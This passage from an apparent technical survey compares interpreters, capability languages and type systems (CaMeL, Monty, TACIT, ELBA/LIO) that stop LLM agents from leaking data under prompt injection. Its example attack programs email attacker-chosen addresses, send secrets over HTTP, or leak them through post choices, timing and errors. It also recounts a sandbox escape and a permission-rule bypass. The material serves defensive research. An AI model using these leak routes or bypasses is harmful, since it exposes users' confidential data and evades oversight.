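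The theorem is a form of noninterference for programs whose results depend partly on chance, as they do when a model writes some of them. Take two runs of a program whose inputs differ only in data that a certain observer may not see. Let $\mu_0(q)$ and $\mu_1(q)$ be the probabilities that the runs finish with an outcome that looks like $q$ to the observer. Then there is a single function $\omega$ such that, for every $q$,

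$$\mu_0(q) \le \omega(q), \qquad \mu_1(q) \le \omega(q), \qquad \text{and} \quad \sum_q \omega(q) \le 1.$$

Suppose that, with one version of the roadmap, a program always finishes and posts "on schedule" 60% of the time and "another week" 40% of the time. These probabilities add up to 1, so $\omega$ must equal them. With any other roadmap, the program can't post either sentence more often, and it can post one less often only by sometimes failing to finish, which includes being halted for breaking the policy. If the program always finishes with both versions of the roadmap, the probability of each sentence is the same for both. Applied to trust labels, the same theorem means that changing the vendor's offer can't alter any result labelled trusted, except by keeping the program from finishing.

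The proof uses a second set of evaluation rules that skip any computation as soon as its label rises above what the observer may see. Runs under these rules never use the hidden data, so they give the same probabilities for both inputs. They also reach each visible outcome at least as often as the real program does, which makes those probabilities the required $\omega$. Garby and colleagues checked the proof in Lean. They also wrote the interpreter in Lean and proved that its results have the probabilities that the evaluation rules assign.

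The theorem holds even if the model is dishonest or incompetent, and a reply may contain any text. But it assumes that each reply is drawn at random from a fixed distribution that depends only on the conversation so far. A model service that carried information from one conversation into another would violate that assumption. The proof also doesn't cover the code that contacts the service.

Tools are a larger limitation. In LLMbda they are functions that update a record inside the program, and the theorem covers only the final record. Real tools act as soon as the program calls them. A program could post 1, 2, 3 and so on, and stop when it reaches a secret number. Under the theorem, this is one run that failed to finish, but anyone who saw the posts would know the number.

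The developer must also label every source correctly and put the right check on every sensitive tool. Garby and colleagues built a banking agent called Randori with deliberately simplified policies. Its `send_money` tool requires a trusted recipient, but `schedule_transaction` checks only the amount. The theorem holds for both tools because it guarantees only that the labels are sound.

### Exceptions and the evidence from Randori

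LLMbda has an `endorse` operation that marks a value as trusted, for legitimate tasks that act on untrusted data, such as paying the bill in a file. A second theorem guarantees that endorsing a value cannot expose a secret, whatever untrusted inputs the attacker chooses. Endorsement can still let an attacker influence an action, so Garby and colleagues suggest endorsing only a choice from a short fixed list, much as APPA does. If the list has $n$ options, the attacker controls at most $\log_2 n$ bits.

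Randori avoids the leaks caused by CaMeL's retries by letting the planner test its program on invented data. In these test runs, tools that would change something do nothing, and reading a file returns placeholder text. The planner corrects the program until it runs without errors, then writes a final version for the real account without having seen any real data. However, the planner cannot fix errors that appear only with real data, or label violations, which the test runs do not raise.

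On AgentDojo's banking tasks, attacks succeeded in two of Randori's 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to follow the payment instructions in a file, the attacker had replaced the file's contents, and the program endorsed the new contents. Labels can't distinguish that attack from the legitimate task, because the user had authorised the agent to base the payment on whatever the file contained.

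The benchmark is a weaker test of tags than these figures suggest. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needs a tool call or file that the planner's program would never include, so keeping the planner away from untrusted text is normally enough to stop it. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL with its policy checks switched off, attacks succeeded in only five of 622 completed runs under attack. With the checks on, they succeeded in none of 588. The case for tags therefore depends more on the reasoning about programs like A and C than on these scores.

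In two of the five successes, the user had asked the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely, so the planner wrote a program that matched each instruction in the file to a tool. The planner never read the file, but the file's contents determined which tools ran. Separating the two models does not help if the program gives data this control.

### When a value enters a model's conversation

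Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, raise another objection to CaMeL. Tags belong to values in the interpreter, and they disappear once a value enters a model's conversation as text. Suppose the user reads the comparison with the vendor's offer and then asks the agent to write to the contact it mentions. If the planner has the comparison in its conversation, it can copy the address into its next program:

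```python
send_email(to="sales@vendor.example", body=reply)
```

The interpreter now receives the address as a constant in a program from the trusted planner. The address has no tags, so the policy allows the email, even though the vendor chose the address. This does the same thing as program A, but over two requests.

One remedy is to give the planner a placeholder and show the text only to the user, as Odersky and colleagues do in their system. The planner then can't adapt its plan to the text. The alternative is to label the whole conversation, as LLMbda and FIDES do. In LLMbda, the copied address would count as untrusted because the program that contained it ran under the conversation's label. The objection therefore applies to CaMeL's design but not to every interpreter that tracks labels as it runs.

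However, labelling the conversation causes label creep, as it did in FIDES. When one of Garby and colleagues' agents read an email in its main conversation, every part of the reminder it then wrote was labelled untrusted, including the subject. A second agent wrote its program before reading anything, so when the email tool ran its check, only the recipient's address was untrusted, because it came from a quarantined model.

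### Monty

Monty runs a subset of Python using its own instruction set instead of the standard Python interpreter. Pydantic's *Security Model* explains that Monty has no instruction for opening a file or a network connection. This is stronger than blocking those operations, because a program can't find a hidden way to reach them. By default, programs can read the clock and get random numbers, but the developer can change both settings. Freezing the clock stops a program from measuring elapsed time.

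An agent's program can affect the outside world only through functions, objects and folders that the developer supplies. When the program calls one of these functions, Monty pauses and gives the host the function's name and arguments. The host runs the function and resumes the program with the result. According to Pydantic's *Monty*, the host can also save the paused program, so a person can take as long as needed to approve a call. If the host shares an object, the program can use only the attributes and methods that the host lists, and the list is empty by default.

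Monty stops program B at the import. It looks for the module among those the developer supplied and in the folders the program may read, and raises an error if it doesn't find it. Monty also raises an error for unknown function names, with "no fallback to a host Python", according to Pydantic's *Built-in functions*.

Program A runs until it calls `send_email`. The host function then receives the recipient's address as an ordinary string, with no record that it came from the offer. That function has the host's full authority, so Pydantic tells developers to validate its arguments like any other untrusted input. A fixed list of recipients would stop A, but it has the same limits here as in any other guard. Program C also runs, because each of its possible posts is a permitted call with a harmless argument. Odersky and colleagues point out that sandboxes in general have this problem, since an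 agent may be allowed to read a private file and to contact a model in the cloud, and can leak the file by doing one after the other.

Monty removes the main weakness of guards, which check only a single call when an agent runs a whole program. Monty passes each tool call inside the program to the host separately, and the program cannot bypass the guard. It also starts in about a millisecond, so a developer can use it for every program an agent writes.

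### A new trusted base

Security now depends on the interpreter being correct. In April 2026 Pydantic offered $5,000 to anyone who could read a secret from a server protected only by Monty. Pydantic's *Hack Monty Postmortem* reports that a researcher succeeded in less than 48 hours, through a memory-safety flaw in a small part of the code that Monty's developers had exempted from Rust's usual memory checks. The company has since fixed the flaw. *Hack Monty 2* (Colvin, 2026) announced a second contest with a $10,000 prize and did not claim that Monty was free of bugs. The page for the core package, Pydantic's *monty*, still describes it as experimental.

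Prefect, which uses Monty in its software, warned in the contest announcement that an escape from an interpreter inside the host process compromises the host. Monty's Python package now runs programs in a separate process that starts without the host's environment variables, where many applications keep passwords. But Monty adds no operating-system restrictions to that process, so code that escapes the interpreter can still use any files and connections available to the process.

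Mistakes in label tracking are harder to notice because the program keeps running normally. Garby and colleagues found that when a CaMeL program inserts an untrusted value into a longer string, the result counts as trusted. Python's f-strings cause the same fault in taint-tracking libraries. An interpreter can avoid it because it evaluates the f-string itself, but only if its author writes the rule for labeling the result correctly. A proof like LLMbda's rules out this kind of mistake, but so far only for a small research language.

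### A smaller language

Leaving a feature out of an interpreter means there is less to check, but a model may still try to use that feature. Monty does not support generator functions, the `del` statement or decorators on methods. In *Running Pydantic’s Monty Rust sandboxed Python subset in WebAssembly*, Willison (2026) noted in February that it didn't support classes either, but thought this hardly mattered because models read the error message and try another way. Monty now supports simple classes, according to Pydantic's *Classes*.

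If the interpreter rejects a program before running it, retrying is harmless because the error reveals nothing about the data. An error during the run can depend on a secret, and CaMeL's retry loop leaks through such errors. The program may also have sent an email before it failed, and the next attempt may send it again. An interpreter that tracks labels should therefore find as many mistakes as possible before the first tool call.

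LLMbda is harder for a model to write, because its syntax was not in any model's training data. In one of Garby and colleagues' examples, GPT-5.2 took three attempts to write a valid factorial function. Randori's prompt includes a grammar and fourteen rules about common mistakes.

CaMeL's version of Python does not let programs define their own functions. Odersky and colleagues argue that this restriction is hard to lift if a checker must also predict, before the program runs, where its data will go. When programs can pass functions to other functions, the checker has to work out which function each call may reach, and a precise analysis can take time that grows exponentially with the program's length. LLMbda allows such functions because it tracks labels only as the program runs. As a result, it may detect a forbidden flow only after earlier tool calls have taken effect.

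## Capability languages checked by a compiler

A compiler can reject a program that breaks the policy before any of its tool calls take effect, provided that the program's text shows what each part can do. The text of a Python program doesn't show this, because any function may import a module and open a connection. In an object-capability language, code can use a power such as network access only if it holds a value that grants it.

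### Authority that follows references

Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained*, explain the idea with two Unix commands that copy a file:

```sh
cp foo.txt bar.txt
cat < foo.txt > bar.txt
```

The `cp` program receives two file names and opens the files itself, so it needs the power to open any file the user might name. When `cat` copies a file through shell redirection, the shell opens both files and passes them to `cat`, which needs no further access. Unix still gives `cat` the user's full authority, while an object-capability system would give it only the two open files.

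In a capability language, files and connections are objects, and code can affect an object only by sending a message through a reference it holds. Code gets references only when it starts, when it creates an object, or in messages from code that already has them. Miller and Shapiro summarize this rule as "only connectivity begets connectivity". A reviewer can therefore trace the references and find everything an agent's program could ever reach. Many object-oriented languages break this rule. C++ code can turn an integer into a pointer, and Java has static variables through which any two pieces of code can communicate. The language E avoids such gaps, and Miller's thesis, *Robust Composition*, describes both E and CapDesk, a desktop built in E to be safe from viruses.

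*Joe-E* (Mettler, Wagner and Close, 2010) creates an object-capability language by removing features from Java. Its verifier rejects source code that defines native methods, keeps mutable data in static variables or uses reflection to access private fields. Any program that passes is still ordinary Java and runs on the standard Java runtime.

Joe-E's verifier also lets a program refer only to the parts of the Java library that Joe-E's designers have approved. Choosing those parts was slow and risky. Java's `File` object has a method that returns the parent directory, so a program with access to one file could reach the root of the disk. One constructor opens a named file inside a given directory, but if the directory is null, it accepts any path on the machine. A security review of E's list of approved Java methods had found several that should have been left off. Mettler and colleagues call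 this dependence on careful manual selection a substantial weakness.

### Code that has no effects

Suppose the harness lets the agent's program process the roadmap with a function that the program defines, such as one that counts the headings. The harness has to be sure that the function only computes a result and doesn't also send the text somewhere. With run-time capabilities alone, the harness can't tell a function that only counts headings from one that also emails the text to the vendor, because a function keeps the references that were in scope when the program created it, and the language hides those references from other code.

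The harness can't simply remove this hiding, because a mail tool relies on it to keep its network connection from the agent. Miller and Shapiro's model allows the harness to request the function's source code and load it with no references. But the harness can't verify that a function the program has already created is harmless.

Joe-E solves part of the problem with static checks. If a programmer marks a type as `Immutable`, the verifier makes sure that its objects contain nothing changeable, however deeply nested. Mettler and colleagues' example is a plugin that decodes images and exchanges only arrays of bytes with its host. A malicious decoder can return the wrong picture, but it can't use the network or remember one image while it decodes the next. Finifter, Mettler and colleagues had already worked on this kind of guarantee in *Verifiable functional purity in java* (2008). Odersky and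 colleagues therefore overstate the case when they describe Joe-E as relying on run-time mechanisms alone. But the marking is all or nothing, so a programmer can't use it to specify that a function may use the log file and no other resource.

### Capture sets

Scala 3 has an experimental capture checker that puts this information into types. Besides its usual description of a value, a type has a capture set, which lists the capabilities that the value may hold. If `log` is a capability for a file, the compiler gives these two functions different types:

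```scala
(s: String) => log.write(s)   // String ->{log} Unit
(s: String) => s.length       // String -> Int
```

`Unit` means that the function returns no useful value. The set `{log}` on the arrow shows that the function can use the log file. A plain `->` means that the set is empty, and such a function is called pure. In a type, `=>` means that the function may hold any capabilities.

A value that holds fewer capabilities is acceptable wherever the program expects one that may hold more. If $T^{C}$ is the type $T$ with capture set $C$, and $<:$ means "is acceptable in place of", then

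$$C_1 \subseteq C_2 \;\Rightarrow\; T^{C_1} <: T^{C_2}.$$

The compiler rejects a function of type `String ->{log} Unit` where a pure function is required. Wrapping a capability in another object doesn't hide it, because the object's type also lists the capability. For example, a logger that writes to `log` has the type `Logger^{log}`. The set in braces in a function's type also includes capabilities that the function uses only on a branch that never runs.

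The compiler infers most of these capture sets, so programmers don't have to write them. After ordinary type checking, it goes through the program again, works out how the sets constrain one another and solves the constraints. According to *What's in the Box* (2025), this took less than 15% of the total compilation time for Scala's standard library.

Earlier capability languages had to ban global capabilities, so programs passed each one through every function on the way to the code that needed it. Scala can allow a global console object because any function that uses it has the console in its capture set.

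### TACIT's wrapper for confidential data

Odersky and colleagues used capture checking to build TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types), a server that takes Scala programs from an agent. The compiler checks each program, and the server runs only those that pass. Programs can reach files, commands and the network only through a small library.

TACIT trusts the agent's model less than CaMeL trusts its planner. The model runs in someone else's cloud, and Odersky and colleagues assume that it may cooperate fully with an attacker. Confidential text must never reach it, although a separate local model may read such text. The library therefore returns confidential files inside a wrapper:

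```scala
trait Classified[+T]:
  def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`T` and `U` stand for any types. The program can use `map` to apply a function to the hidden value, and `map` wraps the result too. The thin arrow means the function must be pure, so it can count or rearrange the text but has no capability that would let it send the text anywhere.

If the program prints a wrapped value, the user's terminal shows the content and the agent receives only `Classified(****)`. The value stays wrapped in later requests, so the agent can keep working with a summary it has never seen. TACIT thus avoids the loss of tags that occurs when a value enters a model's conversation.

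### File access that ends with its block

To use ordinary files, a program opens a block of code for one directory:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/work") {
  access("/work/notes.txt").read()
}
```

Inside the block, the program has a capability for that directory. The compiler rejects a program that would keep the capability by returning a function that reads a file later, because the function's capture set would have to name the capability, and that name has no meaning outside the block. In one of Odersky and colleagues' runs, the compiler rejected for the same reason a program that would have returned a list of file handles. Opening the block requires a capability for input and output, so a program can't open it inside `map`.

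The library, not the compiler, checks the paths, and it raises an error at run time if one lies outside the chosen directory. But the agent's program chooses that directory, so the developer has to make the library block any directories that are off limits altogether.

### Safe mode

All this works only if a program cannot make the compiler lose track of a capability. Ordinary Scala has several features that can do so, and TACIT compiles agents' programs in a stricter mode. Scala's *Safe Mode* lists six restrictions:

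1. The program may not use unchecked type casts or pattern matches, which could give a value a type with too small a capture set.
2. It may not use the `caps.unsafe` module, which contains deliberate exceptions to the tracking.
3. It may not use `@unchecked` annotations, which turn off particular checks.
4. It may not use reflection at run time.
5. It must compile with capture checking turned on, and changes to variables count as effects.
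6. It may use global objects only if their own implementation is safe.

A library meets the last condition if it compiles in safe mode or if a developer marks it `@assumeSafe`. For example, the documentation describes a mail function that asks the user to confirm each message. The agent's program can call this function but not the unrestricted mailer behind it.

Safe mode allows exceptions because almost any operation can fail, even division. An exception can reveal a secret, so TACIT catches exceptions at runtime and converts them to ordinary values, which can stay inside the wrapper.

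### The vendor task in Scala

TACIT's general library has no mail tool, so suppose that a developer adds `emailUser`, which accepts a wrapped text and sends it only to the user. The benign program could then be:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/work") {
  val offer = access("/work/inbox/vendor_offer.txt").read()
  val roadmap = readClassified("/work/internal/roadmap.md")
  val summary = chat(roadmap.map(text =>
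    s"How does the offer fit the roadmap?\n$offer\n$text"))
  emailUser(summary)
}
```

The program compiles. The function passed to `map` only builds a longer string, so it is pure, and `chat` sends the wrapped question to the local model and returns a wrapped answer.

Program B tries to send the roadmap by a direct HTTP request. Safe mode rejects Java's networking classes, so the program has to use the library's `httpPost`. That function needs a network capability and accepts only plain strings, so it can't take the wrapped roadmap. The program can't call `httpPost` inside `map` either, because the function passed to `map` would then hold the network capability, which `map` doesn't allow.

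Program C would have to make its test inside `map` too:

```scala
roadmap.map { text =>
  if text.contains("acquisition")
  then postPublic("Our review will take another week.")
  else postPublic("Our review is on schedule.")
}
```

If `postPublic` needs a capability called `web`, this function has type `String ->{web} Unit`, and the compiler rejects it because `map` requires `String -> Unit`. The program can compute the test inside the wrapper, but the result stays wrapped, so an `if` outside can't use it as a plain true-or-false value. The loop that copied the roadmap letter by letter also fails to compile, because it would change a variable outside the function. The compiler doesn't need to label the branch or apply a rule about the branch that doesn't run.

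Program A, which takes the recipient from the offer, is a harder case. Suppose the library also has a general `sendEmail` that takes an address and a body as plain strings. The compiler rejects A because the summary is wrapped, which protects the roadmap, but it would accept the address. The vendor could therefore still choose who received a harmless reply. A developer could wrap the offer too, but that would stop the program from using any address in it, even a legitimate contact's, unless a trusted function checked the address and sent the mail.

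These results hold only if every tool with an outside effect requires a capability. In Odersky and colleagues' version of AgentDojo, the published signature of `sendEmail` requires none. The agent's instructions also say that side effects inside `map` happen immediately, which suggests that the compiler accepts tool calls there. If so, programs A and C would both compile in that version, and its protection would come mainly from hiding untrusted text from the model that writes the programs, as in the dual-LLM pattern. Only one of 1,926 attacks on that version succeeded, when an agent quoted a hotel review that contained the attacker's recommendation.

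### The safety experiment

Odersky and colleagues' main safety test uses a small software project with a directory of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 ordinary user tasks with each of 10 injections, some hidden in code comments and others disguised as system messages or tool errors. In 11 further trials, the user asked for the secrets, either openly or with a pretext such as an emergency password change. Each model ran all 131 trials twice, once with the wrapper and once with the secrets as plain strings. The table shows the percentage of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output.

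| Model | Trials | With wrapper | Without wrapper |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 injections | 100 | 100 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 100 | 81.8 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | all 131 | 100 | 98.5 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 injections | 100 | 97.5 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 100 | 27.3 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | all 131 | 100 | 91.6 |

Only three of the 240 injections succeeded without the wrapper, so they provide little evidence about its effect. The 11 malicious requests are more informative. Without the wrapper, MiniMax revealed secrets in eight of them and Claude in two, and with it neither model revealed any. The wrapper also did not reduce the share of ordinary tasks the agents completed.

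The suite was built to test whether confidential text reaches the agent's output, which is exactly what the types are meant to prevent. A perfect score therefore shows mainly that the implementation works as designed. The suite doesn't test whether an attacker can make the agent misuse a tool, and it would not detect a leak through timing.

The published compiler errors show how the attempts failed. One program tried to print a GitHub key from inside `map`, and another tried to write confidential recommendations to a file from there. The compiler rejected both because each used a function that held a capability where a pure function was required.

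### Checking code or tagging data

Odersky and colleagues present TACIT and CaMeL as opposite approaches to the same problem. CaMeL's interpreter tags data while the program runs, whereas TACIT uses Scala's compiler to check beforehand what code can do. The researchers argue that only TACIT can guarantee that a chosen part of a program has no effects.

They also argue that compiler checking scales better to complex programs. Each function's type specifies which capabilities the function may hold, so the compiler can check one function at a time without tracing data through the whole program. Agents can therefore use recursion and pass functions to other functions, which they can't do in CaMeL.

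The argument is convincing for secrecy, where the compiler rejects program C before any of it runs. It is weaker for trust, because TACIT's library has a single wrapper for all confidential data and its types do not record where data came from. A CaMeL policy, by contrast, can allow an address from the company directory and refuse one from the offer. TACIT's agent may also read untrusted text directly and follow instructions in it, as long as the resulting program compiles. Odersky and colleagues regard the two approaches as complementary and suggest adding run-time policies to the library's functions.

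Wrapping more data doesn't fully solve the problem either. VirtusLab's *Safe Scala an introduction* points out that agents are useful because they can read files and emails, so classifying too much makes them much less useful.

### What the compiler does not control

A pure function can still leak information through how long it runs. Suppose the function passed to `map` runs for a minute if the roadmap mentions an acquisition and otherwise finishes at once. The agent learns from the delay whether the roadmap mentions one, and it could learn more by repeating this with other tests. TACIT does not try to prevent leaks through timing or through programs that never finish.

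External commands are a larger gap because Scala's types don't apply to what another process does once a program starts it. Only the list of permitted commands limits that process. Odersky and colleagues suggest permitting specific commands, such as `git diff` and the build tool `sbt`, and advise adding a sandbox where security is critical. Even a short list needs care because `sbt`, for example, runs code from the project's build files. An agent that can edit those files and then start `sbt` can run code that the capture checker has not checked.

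The library is also part of the trusted base. The compiler assumes that code marked `@assumeSafe` is safe, so each use needs a proof or a careful reading. Odersky and colleagues give the example of a cache that stores the results of earlier calls in a mutable variable, which is safe only if the variable never holds anything else. TACIT's reusable library has about 1,000 lines, but the Scala compiler also assumes that the standard-library classes on a built-in list are safe. One wrongly approved method could let a program escape its restrictions, a problem Joe-E's designers also had with the Java library.

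The rest of the trusted base is the compiler, the runtime and the local model, which must not carry text from one request into another. The core of capture checking has machine-checked proofs, but researchers have not yet proved that safe mode as a whole provides its intended guarantees. The Scala documentation still calls capture checking "highly experimental and unstable".

### LACUNA: the scope as a permission set

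TACIT checks a separate program for each request. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) instead puts the model's code inside a developer's existing program. The developer leaves a gap, such as `agent[String]("summarise the findings")`, which states the task and the type of the result. When the program reaches the gap, the model writes Scala code to fill it. The compiler checks that code as if the developer had typed it there, and returns any errors to the model for another attempt.

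The model's code can use the variables and functions that are in scope at the gap. With capture checking on, these form the agent's permission set. If the scope contains the summary and `emailUser` but no general mail or network function, the model can email the summary to the user but cannot write program A or B. To narrow the scope, the developer can move the gap into a separate function, where the model's code can use only the function's parameters and the file's top-level definitions.

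The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole before any of it runs. In one example, the code subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the program expects a number. Python would change the balance before it reached the error, but in LACUNA the balance stays at 100 because the compiler rejects the code. The check protects only against mistakes the compiler can find, and code that compiles may still stop halfway if a server fails to respond.

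LACUNA also removes an inconvenience in TACIT, whose cloud model has to write the function for `map` without seeing the confidential text. In LACUNA, that function can contain a gap, which a trusted local model fills after reading the text. The compiler still requires the completed function to be pure.

Zhao and colleagues recommend safe mode here too. Without it, the model's code can use reflection or start external processes, regardless of what is in its scope.

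On AgentDojo, eight of 1,898 attacks on LACUNA succeeded, seven of them with Gemini 2.5 Pro. Zhao and colleagues explain that the types don't stop an attacker who persuades the model to misuse a capability that the task needs. The compiler enforces the scope of each gap, but the developer has to decide how small that scope should be.

Both designs could in principle use a language other than Scala. LACUNA needs a typed language that tracks effects and lets a running program call the compiler. Odersky and colleagues consider Haskell for TACIT's approach. Haskell can enforce purity but has no built-in object capabilities, so a developer would have to represent each permission in a library's types.

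## A library made complete by its host language

A permission built into a library's types can't restrict a program that is able to bypass the library. Python programs can do this, so labelling libraries and tool wrappers in Python control only the code that uses them. In Haskell, an expression's type shows whether running it can affect the outside world, and the compiler enforces these types. Zhou and colleagues used this property to build ELBA, a Haskell library for writing agents. An agent can write any program, but the program can have only the effects that the developer's own library provides.

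### From an expected type to a running program

The harness starts an agent by calling a function named `agent` with a prompt and a list of definitions that the model may use. The surrounding code also fixes the type of the result. ELBA then works in three steps:

1. It sends the prompt, the definitions and the expected type to the model, which replies with a Haskell program.
2. The type checker tests the program against the expected type. If the program fails, ELBA sends the compiler's error to the model for another attempt.
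3. A Haskell interpreter runs the accepted program, and its result becomes the result of the call.

ELBA retries only after type errors, which appear before the program runs any tool calls, so its retries can't leak data the way CaMeL's can.

The expected type also limits effects. Haskell marks actions on the outside world with `IO`, so reading a file as text has the type `IO String` rather than `String`. Any program that performs an `IO` action also has an `IO` type. Zhou and colleagues give the example of a public calculator whose harness expects an `Int`. If a user asks it to delete the server's files and then compute a factorial, the model may write a program that does both, but the compiler rejects it because its type is `IO Int`.

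### Restricted effects and hidden constructors

Most agents need some effects. The bibliography agent, for instance, has to write DBLP entries to a file without being able to use `writeFile` for invented ones. For this, the developer defines a new effect type, `BibIO`, and a wrapper for genuine entries, `Trusted`. In simplified form, the library begins like this:

```haskell
module Bibliography
  (BibIO, Trusted, dblpSearch, dblpFetchBib, appendToBibFile) where

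newtype BibIO a   = MakeBibIO (IO a)
newtype Trusted a = MakeTrusted a

dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

Other code may use only the names in parentheses, which don't include `MakeBibIO` or `MakeTrusted`, the constructors that create values of the two types. The agent can therefore get a trusted entry only from `dblpFetchBib`, and it can't turn `writeFile` into a `BibIO` action. The harness expects a program of type `BibIO ()`, where `()` means the program returns no useful value. Such a program can combine the library's three functions with any effect-free code, such as code that sorts entries by year.

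Program B, which sends the roadmap by a direct HTTP request, fails in the same way. The standard networking functions have `IO` types, so they don't type-check in a program that is expected to have the developer's own type. The developer therefore doesn't have to find and wrap every function that can open a connection.

An agent's program can also call `agent`, for example to look at one search result before deciding what to do next. The compiler works out the expected type of this inner call from its position in the program, so the sub-agent is under the same policy. The outer program can give a sub-agent a stricter type, but not a looser one.

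Some checks can only be done while the program runs. In ELBA's file library, a program names a file by extending a `Path` value it already holds. The operator that extends the path follows symbolic links and rejects any result outside the original directory. Zhou and colleagues contrast this with permission rules that match the text of shell commands. In March 2026, a fault in Claude Code let chained commands bypass its rules because the matcher checked only the first command.

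In a test of 100 tasks with Claude Sonnet 5, none of the bibliography agent's 925 citations had a wrong author, year or DOI, compared with 19 of 1,002 from an ordinary agent with web search. The design rules out these errors provided that DBLP's own records are right, but the types don't check whether a citation is relevant.

### Safe Haskell

Ordinary Haskell has loopholes that would defeat all of this. The function `unsafePerformIO`, for example, presents an action as a plain value, so a program could hide a call to `writeFile` inside what looks like a calculation. Terei, Mazières and colleagues (2012), in *Safe Haskell*, describe a restricted form of the language that closes such loopholes. Their example is a plugin that may use only two file functions, both of which check the path. Without the restrictions, a malicious plugin could escape in at least four ways:

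- It could use `unsafePerformIO`.
- It could import a function from another language, such as C, and falsely declare that the function has no effects.
- It could supply a false description of a type, so that a conversion function treats an `IO` action as a permitted one.
- It could use Template Haskell, an extension that generates code during compilation, to reach a hidden constructor.

Safe Haskell blocks all four. It also stops safe code from importing a module unless the compiler has checked that module or its author has marked it as trustworthy. The mark lets a library use unsafe features behind a safe interface, but the compiler doesn't check that the interface is safe. In 2012, about two-thirds of the modules in Haskell's base package needed the mark, so those modules are part of the trusted base, along with the compiler and the runtime.

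Safe Haskell provides strict type safety, on which developers can build their own sandboxes, according to the *Safe Haskell* page in the manual for GHC, the main Haskell compiler. It is not a sandbox by itself, since a safe program of type `IO` can still delete all of a user's files. It also doesn't limit memory or processor time. Compiling hostile code is also risky, because some extensions run code or read files during compilation. Terei and colleagues don't formally guarantee that they found every loophole.

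Zhou and colleagues point out that a compiler flag can restrict agents' code to this safe subset. Their guarantee needs such a restriction, so the condition of Safe Haskell matters. In *Safe Haskell?*, a mailing-list discussion from 2021, one participant reported that the compiler did not guarantee the absence of `unsafeCoerce`, which converts a value to any type, and suggested removing Safe Haskell to save maintenance work. In the same discussion, Eisenberg (2021) called the feature a "slightly-crumbling earthen rampart" and concluded that it needed renovation as part of a larger security overhaul. Hécate (2022), in *Deprecating Safe Haskell, or heavily investing in it?*, asked again whether it was worth keeping. Smith (2022), a former user, replied that the drawbacks outweighed the benefits, but added that strict type safety made restricted effect types work.

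Python's `rexec` had a similar maintenance problem before van Rossum disabled it. Safe Haskell starts from a better position because it only has to close loopholes in the type system, but its developers still have to check each new language feature.

### LIO's single current label

Restricted effects stop program B but don't track where data came from. ELBA tracks this with LIO, an existing Haskell library that Stefan, Russo and colleagues (2012) describe in *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions*. LIO defines its own effect type and hides the constructor, as `BibIO` does, so an agent's program of this type can reach files, messages and the network only through functions that check labels.

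LIO doesn't attach a label to every value. It keeps one current label for the whole computation, and, as *On Dynamic Flow-Sensitive Floating-Label Systems* (2015) explains, this label protects every value in scope that has no explicit label of its own. If $L_{\text{cur}}$ is the current label, reading data with label $\ell$ changes it to

$$L_{\text{cur}} := L_{\text{cur}} \sqcup \ell,$$

and the program may write to a place with label $\ell$ only if

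$$L_{\text{cur}} \sqsubseteq \ell.$$

The label is attached to the computation rather than the text, so converting the roadmap to bytes can't remove it the way it did in Conti and Russo's library.

The drawback is label creep, since a single secret read restricts everything the program does afterwards. LIO addresses this with `toLabeled`, which runs part of a program as a separate computation. The current label can rise during that computation, but it returns to its old value at the end. The result comes back in a wrapper with its own label. The program can pass the wrapped value around freely, but to read it, the program must call `unlabel`, which raises the current label.

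In ELBA, a program can run a sub-agent inside `toLabeled`. The sub-agent reads an untrusted document and returns a wrapped answer that the outer agent can pass on without seeing it. The sub-agent resembles CaMeL's quarantined model, but it keeps its tools, and LIO checks each tool call against the raised label. This also answers the objection that CaMeL's tags disappear when a value enters a model's conversation. A prompt is a plain string, so the program has to unwrap the text before a model can read it, and any code the model then writes runs under the raised label.

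### Programs A and C under LIO

LIO accepts any lattice of labels, including the pairs of trust and secrecy used for FIDES, such as $(U, H)$ for untrusted and secret. Suppose that `sendEmail` takes a plain address and a wrapped body, much as ELBA's tool for direct messages does. It requires the current label to be trusted and the recipient to be allowed to read the body, but the body itself may be untrusted. Program A, which takes the recipient from the offer, then becomes:

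```haskell
do summary <- toLabeled (U, H) (do
     offer   <- readDoc "inbox/vendor_offer.txt"
     roadmap <- readDoc "internal/roadmap.md"
     askModel question [offer, roadmap])
   found <- toLabeled (U, L) (do
     offer <- readDoc "inbox/vendor_offer.txt"
     askModel "Who should get the comparison?" [offer])
   address <- unlabel found
   sendEmail address summary
```

The label after `toLabeled` sets an upper limit on what the block may read and becomes the label of its result. The current label changes as follows:

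| Step | Current label | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Start | $(T, L)$ | |
| First block reads the offer | $(U, L)$ | |
| First block reads the roadmap | $(U, H)$ | |
| First block ends | $(T, L)$ | `summary`, labelled $(U, H)$ |
| Second block reads the offer | $(U, L)$ | |
| Second block ends | $(T, L)$ | `found`, labelled $(U, L)$ |
| `unlabel found` | $(U, L)$ | a plain address |
| `sendEmail` | $(U, L)$ | refused, because U is not allowed |

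The model can't leave out `unlabel`, because the compiler rejects a wrapped address where `sendEmail` expects a plain one. The benign program has only the first block and then emails the user. Its current label is $(T, L)$ when it sends the email, so LIO allows it.

Program C posts one of two fixed sentences depending on the roadmap:

```haskell
do roadmap <- readDoc "internal/roadmap.md"
   if "acquisition" `isInfixOf` roadmap
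     then postPublic "Our review will take another week."
     else postPublic "Our review is on schedule."
```

The current label starts at $(T, L)$. It rises to $(T, H)$ on the first line, before the program tests anything, and stays there in both branches. A public post requires $L_{\text{cur}} \sqsubseteq (T, L)$, so LIO blocks it whichever branch runs.

The program could instead run the test inside `toLabeled`, but the result would be a wrapped Boolean, which `if` doesn't accept. Unwrapping it would raise the current label to $(T, H)$ again. The program could also try to leak the answer by raising an error inside the block only if the roadmap mentions an acquisition, and then posting publicly after the block. If the error stopped the whole program, the missing post would reveal the secret. LIO prevents this by catching the error at the edge of the block and storing it in the wrapped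 result, so the post appears either way.

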